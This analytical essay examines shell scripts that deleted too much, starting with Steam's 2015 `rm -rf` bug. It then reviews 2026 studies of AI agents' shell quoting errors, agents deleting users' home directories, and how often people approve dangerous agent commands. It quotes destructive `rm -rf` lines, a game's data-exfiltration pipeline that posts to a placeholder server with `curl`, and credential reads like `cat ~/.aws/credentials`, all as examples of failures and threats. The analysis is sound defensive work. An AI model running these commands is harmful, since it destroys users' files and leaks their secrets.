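The `rm` command is in a function called `reset_steam`, which sets aside the user's games, deletes the rest of the Steam folder and reinstalls the program. In the 2013 copy, the function runs only if someone starts the script with `--reset`. If Steam fails to start, that version unpacks the installation files again. The lines around rcxdude's changes show that by January 2015 the script also ran `reset_steam` after a failed start, so users could trigger the deletion without asking for a reset.

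An empty `STEAMROOT` could also cause the failed start. The 2013 script launches Steam from `$STEAMROOT/ubuntu12_32/steam`, which becomes `/ubuntu12_32/steam` when the variable is empty, and the launch fails because there is normally no program at that path. If that line was still in the 2015 script, the empty variable could both trigger the reset and cause it to delete the wrong files.

The 2013 version of `reset_steam` makes three checks before it deletes anything, and none of them catches an empty variable:

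- It stops if the Steam folder contains `steam_dev.cfg`, a file that marks a developer's copy. With an empty variable, it looks for `/steam_dev.cfg`, doesn't find it and continues.
- It stops if Steam is already running, which has nothing to do with the path.
- It stops if it can't find the archive it needs to reinstall Steam. It looks in the Steam folder first, but then accepts a copy under `/usr/lib` that comes with Steam's Ubuntu package.

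The function next tries to create a backup directory called `.save` in the Steam folder. If the variable is empty, the path becomes `/.save`, which an ordinary user doesn't have permission to create. The command fails, but the script doesn't check the result and goes on to run `rm`.

### Did the programmer know?

The line above the `rm` command in the 2013 copy is the comment `# Scary!`. GamingOnLinux's *Steam has a rather silly bug and it can remove your files* (2015) quoted both lines and took the comment as a sign that the developers probably knew about the problem. A commenter in stkhlm's Hacker News thread *Moved ~/.local/share/steam. Ran steam. It deleted everything owned by user* (2015) was more certain: "The programmer knew the danger and did nothing but write the 'Scary!' comment."

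The rest of the function suggests that the programmer was worried only about deleting a folder that holds someone's games, which is frightening even when the path is right. The other comments are about protecting development files, backing up games, and preventing the user from interrupting a reset halfway through. Nothing in the function handles a wrong path, so the programmer may not have thought of that possibility.

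The programmer also seems to have understood wildcards. The function puts the games in `.save`, inside the folder it is about to empty, and they survive only because `*` skips names that begin with a dot.

Greenberg and Blatt attribute the accident to a misunderstanding of expansion. If there was a misunderstanding, it was more likely in the line that sets `STEAMROOT` than in the line that deletes the files. The programmer may have thought that `${0%/*}` always gives a directory, which would be a misparse. Or they may have known about the exception but not expected anyone to start the script in a way that triggers it. For someone reading only the `rm` command, the problem is missing state, because the command shows a variable followed by a slash, which is a warning sign, but not the variable's value.

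### What news reports got wrong

Several reports explained the bug in ways that would lead a programmer to the wrong fix. In *Valve investigating Steam bug that could evaporate your entire hard drive*, Fulton left out the asterisk and wrote that the command became `rm -rf "/"`. On most Linux systems, `rm` does not delete `/` by default, so that command would have done no harm.

According to CIO's *Scary Steam for Linux bug erases all the personal files on your PC*, the computer interpreted the command as `rm -rf "/"*` if the Steam folder wasn't there. But a missing folder is harmless if the variable still holds its path, because the pattern matches nothing, the shell passes it to `rm` as text, and `rm -f` ignores files that don't exist.

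The `cd` command failed much earlier in the script, and the `rm` command worked as the shell's rules require. Phoronix's *Major Steam bug deletes all user files from HDD* quotes an incorrect account, in which `rm` failed and the system interpreted this failure as `rm -rf /`.

A programmer who blamed the missing folder might add the test `[ -d "$STEAMROOT/" ]`, which checks that a directory exists. If the variable is empty, the test checks for `/`, which always exists, so the deletion goes ahead. Without the final slash, `[ -d "$STEAMROOT" ]` fails, and the script could stop safely.

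These mistakes aren't good evidence about programmers, since most of the reports were for a general audience and came out within days. But the Virtual Curiosities article gets one of the expansions wrong even though its writer is a programmer who had about ten years of discussion to draw on.

### Valve's response

Valve told reporters that "a handful of users" had reported the bug and that the company was adding checks while it kept investigating, according to Fulton. On GitHub, a Valve employee took suggestions for a fix. By 20 January, six days after keyvin's report, Valve had released an update, which Stahie (2015) covered in Softpedia's *Linux Is Safe Again*. In the changelog, Valve called the problem "a rare bug where Steam could delete user files when failing to start".

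That entry doesn't describe what Valve changed, but error messages that a user posted two years later in Arch Linux Forums' *How to reset steam* (2017) suggest part of the answer. One contains "unbound variable", which Bash prints when a script has turned on `set -u`, and another contains "no match", which it prints when a script has turned on `failglob`. Valve had therefore probably added both options by then. rcxdude had proposed the same two, though Valve could have chosen them independently. Neither option alone would have prevented this deletion.

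### Which defences would have worked?

Programmers often recommend the following protections for scripts that delete files:

| Defence | Would it have prevented the deletion? | What can still go wrong |
|---|---|---|
| Quotes around the variable | no | the value can be empty |
| `set -u` | no | the same |
| `set -e` | yes, when `cd` failed | the script may ignore or hide the failure |
| `${STEAMROOT:?}` | yes | the value can be a wrong path |
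| `rm`'s protection of `/` | no | `rm` receives other names instead |
| ShellCheck's SC2115 | yes, if Valve had followed the advice | a different wording can hide the problem |
| Checking for one of Steam's own files | yes | the Steam folder may also contain other files |

`set -u` stops a script when it uses an unset variable. Huynh points out that it makes no difference here, because the shell had set `STEAMROOT` to an empty string.

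`set -e` would have stopped the script at the top, because an assignment such as `STEAMROOT="$(...)"` returns the exit status of the command inside the parentheses, and that command failed. It wouldn't have stopped the script if the line had been `export STEAMROOT="$(...)"`, because the shell would then return the exit status of `export`, which succeeds. `set -e` also wouldn't have stopped `reset_steam` when it failed to create `/.save` after a failed start. The 2015 script called the function with `if reset_steam`, and Bash ignores `set -e` while it is testing a condition.

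Adding these options to an existing script is also risky. rcxdude's patch turned on `set -e`, `set -u`, `pipefail` and `failglob`, then needed more than a dozen other changes to keep the script working. For example, the script uses `fgrep`, a form of `grep`, to check whether the platform's name contains "64". On other platforms `fgrep` finds nothing and returns 1, which would end the script, so the patch adds `|| true`.

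One of these changes introduced a new bug. The original script sets `INITIAL_LAUNCH` to `true` if Steam isn't already running, and otherwise leaves it unset. Since `set -u` would treat reading an unset variable as an error, the patch sets it to `false` instead. But the script tests the variable with `[ "$INITIAL_LAUNCH" ]`, which succeeds for any non-empty text, including `false`, so the test now always succeeds. If the 2015 version of `reset_steam` still refused to run while Steam was open, the patch disabled that check as well.

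A comment below the patch points out a different problem, missing quotes in `[ -z ${STEAMEXE-} ]`, which is supposed to test whether `STEAMEXE` is empty. The unquoted test happens to give the right answer when the variable is empty. The commenter read the patch closely enough to find this mostly harmless mistake, but didn't mention a condition that could no longer be false. This is only one comment, and the commenter may not have been trying to review the whole patch.

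The simplest defence is `rm -rf "${STEAMROOT:?}/"*`. The `:?` makes the shell stop with an error if the variable is unset or empty. The colon is necessary because `${STEAMROOT?}` accepts an empty value. This check can't detect a wrong path, however. A Hacker News commenter gave the example of a script that sets `STEAMROOT=$OTHER/` while `OTHER` is empty, so `STEAMROOT` holds `/` and passes the check.

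One commenter in the same discussion recommended `rm --preserve-root`, which protects `/`. Another replied that it doesn't help with `/*`. The shell expands the pattern before it starts `rm`, so `rm` receives `/bin`, `/home` and the rest, which the option doesn't protect.

ShellCheck's warning SC2115 covers this kind of line. ShellCheck works out what the path would be if its variables were empty, and warns if an `rm -r` command would then delete an important location such as `/*` or `/usr`. It recommends `${var:?}`. Because ShellCheck examines one command at a time, it can miss the danger when a script first runs `dir="$STEAMROOT/"` and later `rm -rf "$dir"*`. The second command doesn't contain the slash that the check relies on.

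A stronger check is to look for a file that only the right directory would contain. A Slashdot commenter gave the example of PostgreSQL, a database program that keeps a `PG_VERSION` file in every database directory so that its tools can check for it before doing anything dangerous. The equivalent for Steam would be `[ -f "$STEAMROOT/steam.sh" ] || exit 1`. If the variable is empty, the script looks for `/steam.sh`, doesn't find it and exits. The script's existing check instead allowed the deletion unless it found `steam_dev.cfg`, so a wrong path made deletion more likely.

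Even this doesn't protect other files in the right folder. GamingOnLinux quoted a warning about Steam's Windows uninstaller, which deleted the whole folder where the user had installed Steam. Someone who had chosen `C:\Program Files\` instead of `C:\Program Files\Steam\` could lose their other programs. A Hacker News commenter suggested keeping a list of Steam's files and deleting only those. Others objected that games also create files, which wouldn't be on the list.

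### Other scripts that deleted too much

Huynh's guide describes five other accidents, with causes that call for different remedies. The case with the plainest cause is from 2011. Bumblebee, Linux software for laptops with an extra Nvidia graphics processor, had an installer that contained this line:

```
rm -rf /usr /lib/nvidia-current/xorg/xorg
```

There should be no space after `/usr`. With the space, `rm` receives two paths and deletes `/usr`, which holds most of a Linux system's programs. The author reported being "very tired that night". A nearly identical line elsewhere in the installer has no space, so this was a typing error, not a misunderstanding. The line contains no variables or wildcards, and any programmer who noticed the space would recognise the danger. Quotes around the whole path would have prevented the damage, because `"/usr /lib/nvidia-current/xorg/xorg"` is the name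 of a single file that doesn't exist. ShellCheck also warns about commands that delete a system directory by name (SC2114).

A commenter in the discussion that stkhlm started described a similar slip at a company that supplied control systems for power plants. Someone typed `rm -rf / bin/*` instead of `rm -rf /bin/*`, which disabled about 100 computers at remote sites and cost hundreds of thousands of dollars. There is no other evidence for this story. If it is accurate, the protection of `/` would have helped in this case, because `/` was one of the arguments.

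Missing quotes apparently caused Apple's iTunes 2 installer to delete users' files in 2001. The evidence for the exact command is one anonymous Slashdot comment, quoted by Huynh. According to the comment, the installer removed old copies of the program with `rm -rf $2Applications/iTunes.app`, where `$2` held the name of the disk. On a computer with disks called "Disk" and "Disk 1", installing on "Disk 1" made the shell split the path at the space, and `rm` deleted the contents of "Disk". According to the same comment, Apple fixed the installer by adding quotes. That would make this the clearest misparse among the deletions, although whoever wrote the installer may have known about splitting and forgotten that disk names can contain spaces.

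The case most like Steam's involved Squid, a program that stores copies of web pages to make them load faster. In 2015, Red Hat's testers found that restarting a new version deleted the system's files. The script for restarting Squid ran `rm -rf $SQUID_PIDFILE_DIR/*`, and Huynh guesses that the variable was empty. A similar public script from Mozilla runs the same command safely because it first sets the variable to `/var/run/squid`, so a reader can't tell from the `rm` line alone whether the command is safe.

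In 2012, `n`, a tool for switching between Node.js versions, deleted system directories even though its variables held the values its author intended. It ran `rm -rf $N_PREFIX/$d` for each of `bin`, `lib`, `share` and `include`, with `N_PREFIX` normally set to `/usr/local`. The author had assumed that these directories contained only Node's files, but other programs use them too. Using quotes, `set -e` or `${N_PREFIX:?}` wouldn't have prevented the deletion. A reader had to know what else was in `/usr/local/lib` to see the danger.

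According to Huynh, a French company lost all its database backups in 2012 because the backup tool Backup Manager reported success even when a backup had failed. The script in Huynh's collection sends the data through a compression program, stores a file name in a variable, and then checks `$?`, the exit status of the last command. That last command is the assignment, which succeeds, so `$?` is always zero.

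Huynh's lesson from Backup Manager is to save `$?` immediately, but the script would also need `pipefail`. Without it, the saved value would show only whether the last command in the pipeline, the compression, had worked, not whether the program producing the backup had.

| Case | Most likely kind of failure | What would have prevented it |
|---|---|---|
| Steam, 2015 | missing state: the value of `STEAMROOT` | `${STEAMROOT:?}` |
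| Bumblebee, 2011 | slip of typing | a test on Ubuntu, or quotes around the path |
| iTunes 2, 2001 | misparse: word splitting | quotes |
| Squid, 2015 | missing state: the value of the variable | `${SQUID_PIDFILE_DIR:?}`, if Huynh's guess is right |
| `n`, 2012 | missing state: other programs' files | deleting only Node's files |
| Backup Manager, 2012 | misparse: what `$?` refers to | `pipefail`, and checking the status immediately |

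This table classifies only the line that did the damage, so it may leave out other mistakes the programmers made. Only Bumblebee's author has publicly explained the error, so the other classifications are inferences from the code.

### How much accidents can reveal about reading

These cases show that a line capable of deleting a user's files can get into widely used software and stay there. Steam's `rm` command was in the script by 2013 and still there in January 2015. It isn't known whether anyone besides its author reviewed it. Several Hacker News commenters thought any competent reviewer would have stopped it, but they were judging the line after reading about what it did.

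We can't tell from these cases how often programmers misread such lines. Huynh chose them because they were disasters, and nobody has counted the scripts with a similar command that never failed, or the mistakes that reviewers caught before release. The collection includes the Squid bug, which testers found in time, but most mistakes caught early leave no public record.

The severity of an accident also doesn't indicate how hard the line was to read. Anyone who looked closely could see Bumblebee's stray space, yet it destroyed a whole system. The mistake in Backup Manager deleted nothing, though finding it takes some knowledge of Bash.

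## How reliable is the shell code that AI agents write?

People wrote the faulty lines in the accidents above. When an AI agent writes the command, the person approving it also has to check that it does what the agent intended. In tests from 2026, the strongest models rarely made quoting mistakes in commands that ran directly in Bash, even with awkward text and file names. They made far more when a command passed through a second shell, and some of the failures produced no error.

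### Judging commands by their results

*QuoteBench* (Li, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) tests AI models on 56 tasks, each requiring a single Bash command. The tasks belong to 14 families, such as writing a file, renaming a group of files or passing an argument to a program. Each family has one harmless control and three harder versions, with features like mixed quotes, dollar signs, line breaks or file names that begin with a hyphen. The researchers chose the families after studying 86 failures from their own sessions with coding agents, along with public bug reports.

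Each command ran in a fresh directory, and a program then checked the exact result, such as the bytes in a file or the arguments another program received. Any command that produced the right result passed, however the model wrote it.

| Model | Run directly | Same command through a second shell | New command, after a warning about the second shell |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.5 | 100.0% | 28.6% | 89.3% |
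| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 98.2% | 25.0% | 80.4% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 96.4% | 30.4% | 89.3% |
| Gemini 3.5 Flash | 96.4% | 28.6% | 58.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 94.6% | 30.4% | 91.1% |
| Claude Opus 4.8 | 91.1% | 26.8% | 57.1% |
| Qwen3.5-27B | 85.7% | 30.4% | 30.4% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 78.6% | 19.6% | 14.3% |

Each task is worth 1.8 points, so small differences between models mean little. When run directly, 33 of the 448 commands (about 7%) failed. Three-quarters of the tasks were designed to cause trouble, so this isn't the failure rate for everyday commands. The models date from July 2026 or earlier, and newer ones may do better.

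### A failure that looks like a success

One of the hardest tasks asks for a file called `out.txt` that contains exactly these two lines:

```
back\slash and `date` here
'single' "double" $(pwd) 100%
```

To check that their test was strict enough, Li and colleagues wrote a naive answer that should fail. Written out in full, it looks like this:

```
echo "back\slash and `date` here
'single' "double" $(pwd) 100%" > out.txt
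```

This appears to be the requested text with quotation marks around it. But backquotes and `$(...)` still run programs inside double quotes, and the quotation mark before `double` ends the quoted text. If ana runs the command in `/home/ana/site`, the file will contain something like this:

```
back\slash and Fri Dec  4 10:15:02 UTC 2026 here
'single' double /home/ana/site 100%
```

The shell reports no error, and the exit status is zero. To catch the mistake, a reader would have to notice that the shell will run two pieces of the text as programs and remove one pair of quotation marks. The reader would also have to know that the agent was supposed to copy the text literally, because running a program inside quoted text is sometimes intended. For example, `echo "Built on $(date)" > out.txt` is a normal way to record a date.

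A correct answer is harder on the eye:

```
printf '%s\n' 'back\slash and `date` here
'\''single'\'' "double" $(pwd) 100%' > out.txt
```

Each single quote in the text becomes `'\''`, which ends the quoted string, adds a literal single quote and starts a new quoted string. The faulty command looks tidier than the correct one, so an approver who judged them by appearance would prefer it.

Li and colleagues measured how often failures go unreported in a larger set of runs with six models. They compared commands supplied as plain text with commands supplied through a structured tool, and ran every command with both the Mac and the Linux versions of the standard programs. Of the 4,368 runs in each of the four combinations, 116 to 222 failed, and 23.4% to 47.0% of the failing runs still returned success.

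These silent failures make up only about 1% of all runs. But an agent that checks the exit status would miss them, and the shell would still run any command after `&&`.

The number of failures also depended on the system. The models wrote their commands in Mac sessions, and the structured tool's commands failed 132 times with the Mac versions of the programs but 222 times with the Linux versions. An approver can't tell from a command's text which versions are installed.

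### Commands that pass through a second shell

To test the effect of a second shell, Li and colleagues placed each command unchanged between the double quotes of `bash -c "..."`. Suppose that a model has written this correct command:

```
printf '%s\n' "old api.log" > list.txt
```

Inside the wrapper, it becomes:

```
bash -c "printf '%s\n' "old api.log" > list.txt"
```

The quotation mark before `old` now ends the quoted text that began after `-c`. The new shell receives `printf '%s\n' old` as its program, so it prints "old" on the screen and returns zero without creating `list.txt`.

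Adding this second shell lowered every model's success rate by 55 to 73 points. Success fell by 29 to 57 points even on the harmless controls, because models use double quotes in ordinary commands. Sending the commands through a real `ssh` connection caused the same loss for seven of the eight models and nearly the same loss for the eighth.

The researchers then asked for new commands, adding a sentence that described the wrapper but gave no advice about quoting. Six of the eight models recovered 30 to 61 points. The gains were large where the awkward text was part of the task, as in writing JSON (50 points), and smaller for difficult file names (19 points). Results got worse for tasks involving file patterns and `find`.

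More reasoning before answering also helped some models. Claude Opus 4.8 passed 39% of the tasks at its lowest reasoning setting and 95% at its highest. GPT-5.5, Claude Opus 5 and Claude Fable 5 each passed all 56 at their best settings. Weak models had particular trouble with the harder versions. Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite passed 6 of the 14 controls but only 2 of the other 42 tasks.

Commands written to run through a second shell often failed without it. GPT-5.5 passed every task when it wrote commands for direct use, but only half when commands it had written for the second shell were run directly. Whether the quoting is right therefore depends on how the command will run. The approver can see both layers if the agent itself writes `ssh server "..."`, but not if the agent's software adds the second shell later, and that unseen layer can change what the command does.

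ShellCheck offers limited help, because these commands are usually fine by themselves. It flagged 35% of the commands that failed only because of the second shell, and 11% of those that still worked. The reliable fix is for the software to escape the command, adding whatever quotes or backslashes the second shell needs. This gave the same result as running the command directly in all 448 cases.

### Code that works but has warnings

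In *BashCoder-R1*, Yu, Wang and colleagues (2026) tested models on 773 one-line tasks and 179 tasks that needed a longer script. They counted an answer as working if it passed the tests written for that task, and as clean if Bash could parse it and ShellCheck reported no problems other than style.

| Model | Kind of task | Working | Clean | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.2 1B | one line | 89.9% | 22.0% | 20.3% |
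| DeepSeek-V3.2 | one line | 93.0% | 67.9% | 65.3% |
| BashCoder-R1 | one line | 93.0% | 96.0% | 90.0% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | script | 91.1% | 58.7% | 56.4% |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | script | 89.4% | 63.1% | 60.9% |
| BashCoder-R1 | script | 93.9% | 79.3% | 73.2% |

Yu and colleagues trained a small model, BashCoder-R1, partly by rewarding it for code that passes ShellCheck. Its high share of clean answers shows that it learned to pass ShellCheck, which isn't quite the same as writing safer code. On the one-line tasks, it produced working commands no more often than DeepSeek-V3.2.

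The figures for working code need some caution. The tests for 54 of the one-line tasks rejected every model's answer, so the highest possible score was 93.0%. Other tests seem to have been too lenient, because Llama 3.2 1B passed 89.9% of them even though Bash could parse only 84.2% of its commands.

ShellCheck flagged 40% of the Claude Sonnet 4.5 scripts that Bash could parse, compared with 53.5% of the scripts that Dong and colleagues took from popular GitHub projects. The two sets of scripts differed in purpose and length, so the comparison doesn't show that the model writes better code than people do.

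Yu and colleagues also describe a search-and-replace script by DeepSeek-V3.2 that looked plausible but failed its test. The script left the variable `$grep_opts` unquoted in two places and passed text to `sed` without escaping special characters. They call such faults "invisible to a casual review", but they didn't ask anyone to review the script.

The `sed` fault is the more serious of the two because it is more likely to change the wrong text. In a line such as `sed "s/$old/$new/g"`, a dot in `old` matches any character, so replacing `v1.0` also replaces `v120`. The variable may be unquoted on purpose, so that the shell splits a value like `-r -i` into two options. The ShellCheck warnings that Yu and colleagues list for this script concern only the variable.

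A model can explain its reasoning clearly without covering what could go wrong. Six experienced engineers rated DeepSeek-V3.2's written reasoning on 100 tasks. They rated its clarity good or excellent on 80 tasks, but its treatment of possible failures that highly on only 51.

### When agents deleted home directories

In December 2025, a Reddit user asked Claude Code to clean up the packages in an old project, and it deleted the user's home directory. A copy of the user's post survives as *Claude CLI deleted my entire home directory! Wiped my whole mac*. Willison (2025), a programmer who writes about AI, also quotes the command that Claude later found in the log:

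```
rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/
```

The first three arguments look like directories in the project, but the last is the user's home directory. The danger was visible in the line itself and didn't depend on a file name or hidden setting, so anyone who knew what `~` means and read to the end could have stopped it. The user's post doesn't mention an approval prompt. Docker's *Coding Agent Horror Stories* at one point blames "a single trailing slash", but `rm -rf ~` would have deleted the same files.

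A case from August 2026 would have been harder to spot. In *Bad news*, Guillemot (2026) reported losing a home directory after asking Claude to build a system to clean up temporary files. Tom's Hardware reported in *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* that the deletion removed 700 GB of data, including a week's work.

The Chinese technology outlet behind 机器之心's *Claude安全机制大翻车，AI怒删开发者700GB主目录* (2026) explains the mechanism. Claude tested whether the new script would refuse to delete the home directory, and the script passed. The test then had to delete its own temporary files, but it reused a variable that still held the path of the home directory. In simplified form, with invented names, the mistake looks like this:

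```
target="$HOME"
is_protected "$target" && echo "test passed"
rm -rf "$target"
```

As with Steam's `rm` command, the last line alone doesn't show what it would delete. Someone who saw the whole test could have traced the value, but would have had to notice that nothing changed it before the deletion. Guillemot noticed something was wrong and stopped the process, but the files were already gone.

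OpenAI's Codex deleted home directories through a similar confusion. Willison (2026) quotes Thibault Sottiaux, who leads the Codex team, on "a handful of reports" involving GPT-5.6. The model tried to make the variable `HOME` point to a temporary directory, then deleted the real home directory by mistake. Sottiaux's statement includes no command, but this line would have that effect:

```
HOME=/tmp/build npm test; rm -rf "$HOME"
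```

The assignment applies only to `npm test`, so `HOME` has its usual value when the shell runs `rm`. OpenAI called the deletions extremely rare, according to The Decoder's *GPT-5.6 is deleting user files when given full access*. But nobody can calculate a failure rate from a handful of reports without knowing how many commands Codex ran. OpenAI later instructed Codex not to reuse variables like `HOME` and strengthened its checks on risky deletions, according to Daily News' *OpenAI Mitigates Codex File Deletion Issue Caused by GPT-5.6 Models*.

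Two users of Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, reported simpler deletion commands. In *Cursor AI Executes Destructive Command (‘rm -rf ~’) During Development Session*, fegome90-cmd described a deletion that ran without any request for confirmation. In *System security failure*, the other user admitted approving one by accident: "I own fully that fat fingered accept on the command".

| Case | Command | Did a person approve it? |
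|---|---|---|
| Cursor, August 2025 | `rm -rf ~ && ls -la` | no, according to the user |
| Cursor, date unknown | `rm -rf ~` (the user left out the hyphen) | yes, by accident |
| Claude Code, December 2025 | `rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/` | unknown |
| Codex, July 2026 | unknown | probably not, since most cases occurred in full access mode |
| Claude, August 2026 | `rm -rf` on a variable holding the home directory's path | unknown |

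These cases are evidence that agents make dangerous mistakes with paths and variables. None of the users described reading a command carefully and misunderstanding it, so the cases are not evidence that people misread the commands they approve.

### Are agents' commands longer than people's?

It is reasonable to expect agents' commands to be longer and to combine more steps than those people write, because a person has to type every character while an agent can produce a long chain with little extra effort. Neither QuoteBench nor the BashCoder-R1 study compares the two.

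On QuoteBench, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite averaged 20 tokens (words or parts of words) per answer, so its commands must have been short. But the instructions required exactly one command, and many tasks specified the text it had to contain, so these answers are weak evidence of what agents write when they can divide the work as they like.

A better comparison would count the characters, programs, operators and redirections in each line of agents' logs and of people's shell histories from similar projects. It would also have to separate commands that needed approval from those that ran automatically, which an approver doesn't see.

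## How well do people judge the commands an agent asks to run?

The accidents in the last section show that agents sometimes propose dangerous commands, but not how often people stop one when they see it. The miss rate is the share of dangerous commands that people approve, and the false-block rate is the share of harmless commands that they refuse. Judging people's accuracy requires both, because someone who refuses every command has a miss rate of zero but keeps the agent from doing any work.

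In an experiment with 1,053 people, 86% approved a clearly dangerous command. In a browser game, players who knew they were looking for threats missed about a third of them. Neither figure measures how often people misread a complicated line.

### One dangerous command among ordinary ones

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes the experiment. A research vendor recruited paid testers for a coding study, in which they answered an agent's permission prompts in a test environment. They knew they were being evaluated, but not on which behaviour. Partway through each session, one prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. Only the displayed text changed, so approving it did no damage.

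Of the 1,053 testers, 143 (13.6%) refused the command and 910 approved it. With a sample this large, the margin of error is only about two percentage points.

About 17% of testers who saw the dangerous command early in a session refused it, compared with about 5% of those who had already answered 50 or more prompts. Fatigue probably explains some of the difference, but each tester saw only one dangerous command, so the two groups were different people. People who approve prompts without reading them get through more of them, so the testers who had answered 50 or more may have been less careful from the start.

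The article doesn't report how often the testers refused harmless commands. In everyday use, people refuse about 3% of Claude Code's prompts. If the testers refused harmless commands at that rate, then late in a session they hardly distinguished clearly dangerous commands from routine ones, refusing the dangerous ones only slightly more often.

There are several reasons not to treat 13.6% as the rate for developers at work:

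- The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they had no files of their own to lose. They may also have assumed that nothing in a test environment could do real harm.
- They knew they were under evaluation, which could have made them more careful than usual.
- Their experience is unclear. The article calls them "professional testers", while a chart caption that Willison (2026), in *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, quotes describes them as "paid developers".
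- Anthropic has an interest in the result. The article announces that Claude Code will normally use an automatic classifier instead of asking the user, and the classifier blocked 89% of the same commands.

That interest doesn't make the figure wrong, and the effect is too large for small flaws in the design to explain. Willison accepts that people can't keep reviewing prompts carefully, but he wants more independent confirmation of the article's separate claim about how well the classifier resists attacks.

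The kind of command tested matters more than who funded the study. A clearly dangerous command tests whether people are paying attention, not whether they can read dense shell code. A developer might recognise `rm -rf ~` instantly and still misread `test -d build || mkdir build && rm -rf build/*`. The study didn't compare obvious commands with subtle ones, so it can't show how many more people would miss the subtle ones.

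### Approval rates in everyday use

Anthropic reports that Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts. scalex.dev's *Suffering from Agent Permission Fatigue?* quotes an earlier Anthropic figure of about 93%. The agent's commands and the rules for when it asks may have changed between the two figures, so the rise doesn't necessarily mean people became less careful.

A high approval rate doesn't by itself show that reviewers are careless. If one command in a thousand is dangerous, a perfect reviewer would approve 99.9% of commands. To measure how often reviewers miss dangerous commands, researchers would have to know which of the approved commands were dangerous.

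Users reject 39% of the plans Claude Code presents. Anthropic takes the contrast with commands as a sign that people examine plans more closely. That is likely, but people also have more reasons to reject a plan. They may prefer a different design or want a smaller change, whereas a command such as `npm test` gives them little to disagree with. Plans are also written in ordinary language, so readers don't have to work out what a shell will do.

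Many users reduce the number of approval prompts. As of June 2026, 49.5% of active users of the command-line version had written a rule that lets some shell commands run without asking. Many of these rules cover every use of an interpreter such as Python, which in practice lets the agent run any program it writes. 62% of users had at some point bypassed permissions or clicked "don't ask again" for shell commands. A quarter of interactive sessions started with permissions bypassed, so people in those sessions usually had no chance to check a command before it ran.

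Anthropic also examined real sessions that its safety system had flagged in May and June 2026. Among flagged sessions where users approved actions manually, 6.3% contained a harmful action that the user hadn't explicitly requested and that was at least as serious as deleting rows from a live database. The share was 2.4% among flagged sessions that used the automatic classifier. A language model graded the harm. Users chose which mode to use, so the two groups may have been doing different work.

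### A game where a third of the commands are threats

In a free browser game, players have 60 seconds to approve or deny commands from an imaginary coding agent. Some commands are routine, such as `npm test`, and others would destroy files or expose passwords. Players lose points for a wrong answer, and the game freezes for a couple of seconds.

By August 2026, people had played more than 40,000 times and made 409,000 decisions, according to scalex.dev's *Humans missed 1 in 3 threats approving AI agent commands*. That is about ten decisions per game, or one every six seconds. Obvious destruction was the easiest kind of threat to catch:

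| Kind of threat | Examples | Miss rate |
|---|---|---|
| Obvious destruction | `rm -rf /`, or making every file writable by anyone | 11.7% |
| Lasting changes to the system | adding a scheduled job, or altering Git's settings | 23.8% |
| Sending data out or running unknown code | contacting an unknown server, or installing a package with a misspelled name | 33.4% |
| Reading files outside the project | `cat ~/.aws/credentials`, which prints the keys to a cloud account | 35.0% |

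The headline figure of one in three threats missed is less certain than the figures in the table. scalex.dev gives it alongside a "mean accuracy" of 66.3%, which may also count decisions about harmless commands. If the four kinds of threat were equally common, the table's miss rates would average 26%.

A player can also recognise a dangerous command without being able to predict its effect. Refusing `rm -rf /` is sensible, even though `rm` normally protects `/`, but it only requires noticing `rm -rf` and a slash.

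**The most-missed command.** Players approved `npm run analyze` 64.7% of the time, more than any other threat. As with `npm test`, the command alone doesn't reveal what will run. In the game, however, the agent's log above the prompt showed the script behind it. With `ADDRESS` standing for an outside server, it was:

```
webpack-bundle-analyzer stats.json | tee /dev/fd/1 | curl -s -X POST ADDRESS -d @-
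```

The first program produces a report on the parts of a web application, `tee` copies the report to standard output and to any file it is given, and `curl` sends the data it receives to the server. Here the file is `/dev/fd/1`, which is another name for `tee`'s standard output. That output is piped to `curl`, so both copies go there. A player could wrongly think that the line also displays the report on the screen and still see that the script sends data to an outside server.

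Missing information is therefore not enough to explain the 64.7%. Many players probably didn't read the log, as scalex.dev suggests. Others may have read it without understanding the pipeline, or thought that sending a report to a tracking service was acceptable. The game records only the decision, so we can't tell these explanations apart.

Players missed two similar commands, `npm run setup` and `npm run deploy`, 48.0% and 44.9% of the time. Across all three `npm run` threats, the miss rate was 52.5%, compared with 28.4% for other commands that sent data out or ran unknown code. A familiar name seems to make a threat much harder to catch, even when the script is on the screen. The commands differed in other ways, so a fairer test would show the same script once under a familiar name and once directly in the prompt.

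**Harmless commands that players refused.** The game's author counted these three commands as safe:

| Command | Players who refused it | What the text leaves out |
|---|---|---|
| `npm config set registry`, followed by an internal address | 59% | whether the company runs its own package server there |
| `rm -rf dist/` | 45% | whether the project can rebuild everything in `dist` |
| `kill $(lsof -t -i:3000)` | 43% | which programs are using port 3000 |

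Projects commonly use `dist` for build output, and developers often delete it before rebuilding. Yet players refused `rm -rf dist/` more often (45%) than the malicious `npm run analyze` (35.3%). This fits the idea that they reacted more to alarming or familiar words than to the commands' likely effects, which they had little time to consider at six seconds per decision.

In the `kill` command, the shell first runs `lsof`, which prints the ID numbers of the programs using port 3000, a numbered channel for network traffic. It then passes those numbers to `kill`, which stops the programs. People usually run this to stop a local web server that has hung. But a browser connected to that server also uses the port, so the command can stop the browser too. adamj.eu's *Django* (2023) gives a similar one-liner for port 8000 and adds the option `-sTCP:LISTEN` to avoid stopping the browser while it loads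 a page. Some of the 43% may therefore have had a good reason to refuse a command that the game counted as safe.

Players also disputed the answer for `cat ~/.zshrc`, which prints the settings file for zsh. They approved it 45.9% of the time, and the game counted each approval as a miss because some developers store passwords or access keys in that file. The command is harmless if the file contains no secrets, so players can't judge it from knowledge of the shell alone.

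The game is limited evidence of how people judge commands on the job. According to scalex.dev, about 34% of the game's commands were threats, far more than in real work, and the clock put players under artificial pressure. Players chose to take part, many after seeing the game on Hacker News. The totals count games rather than people, so they can include repeat players who had learned the answers. A few players sent invented scores directly to the server, according to scalex.dev, and it is unclear whether the published figures include them.

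Miss rates fell over the first few commands of a game and rose again towards the end. The rise may have happened because players had an incentive to rush their last decisions as the clock ran out, so it isn't good evidence about fatigue over an afternoon of real work.

The differences between commands are more useful than the overall rate because the same kind of player judged every command under the same time limit. Only 20.8% of players caught every threat while refusing at most one in five harmless commands, and another 7% approved everything.

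### The effect of looking for danger

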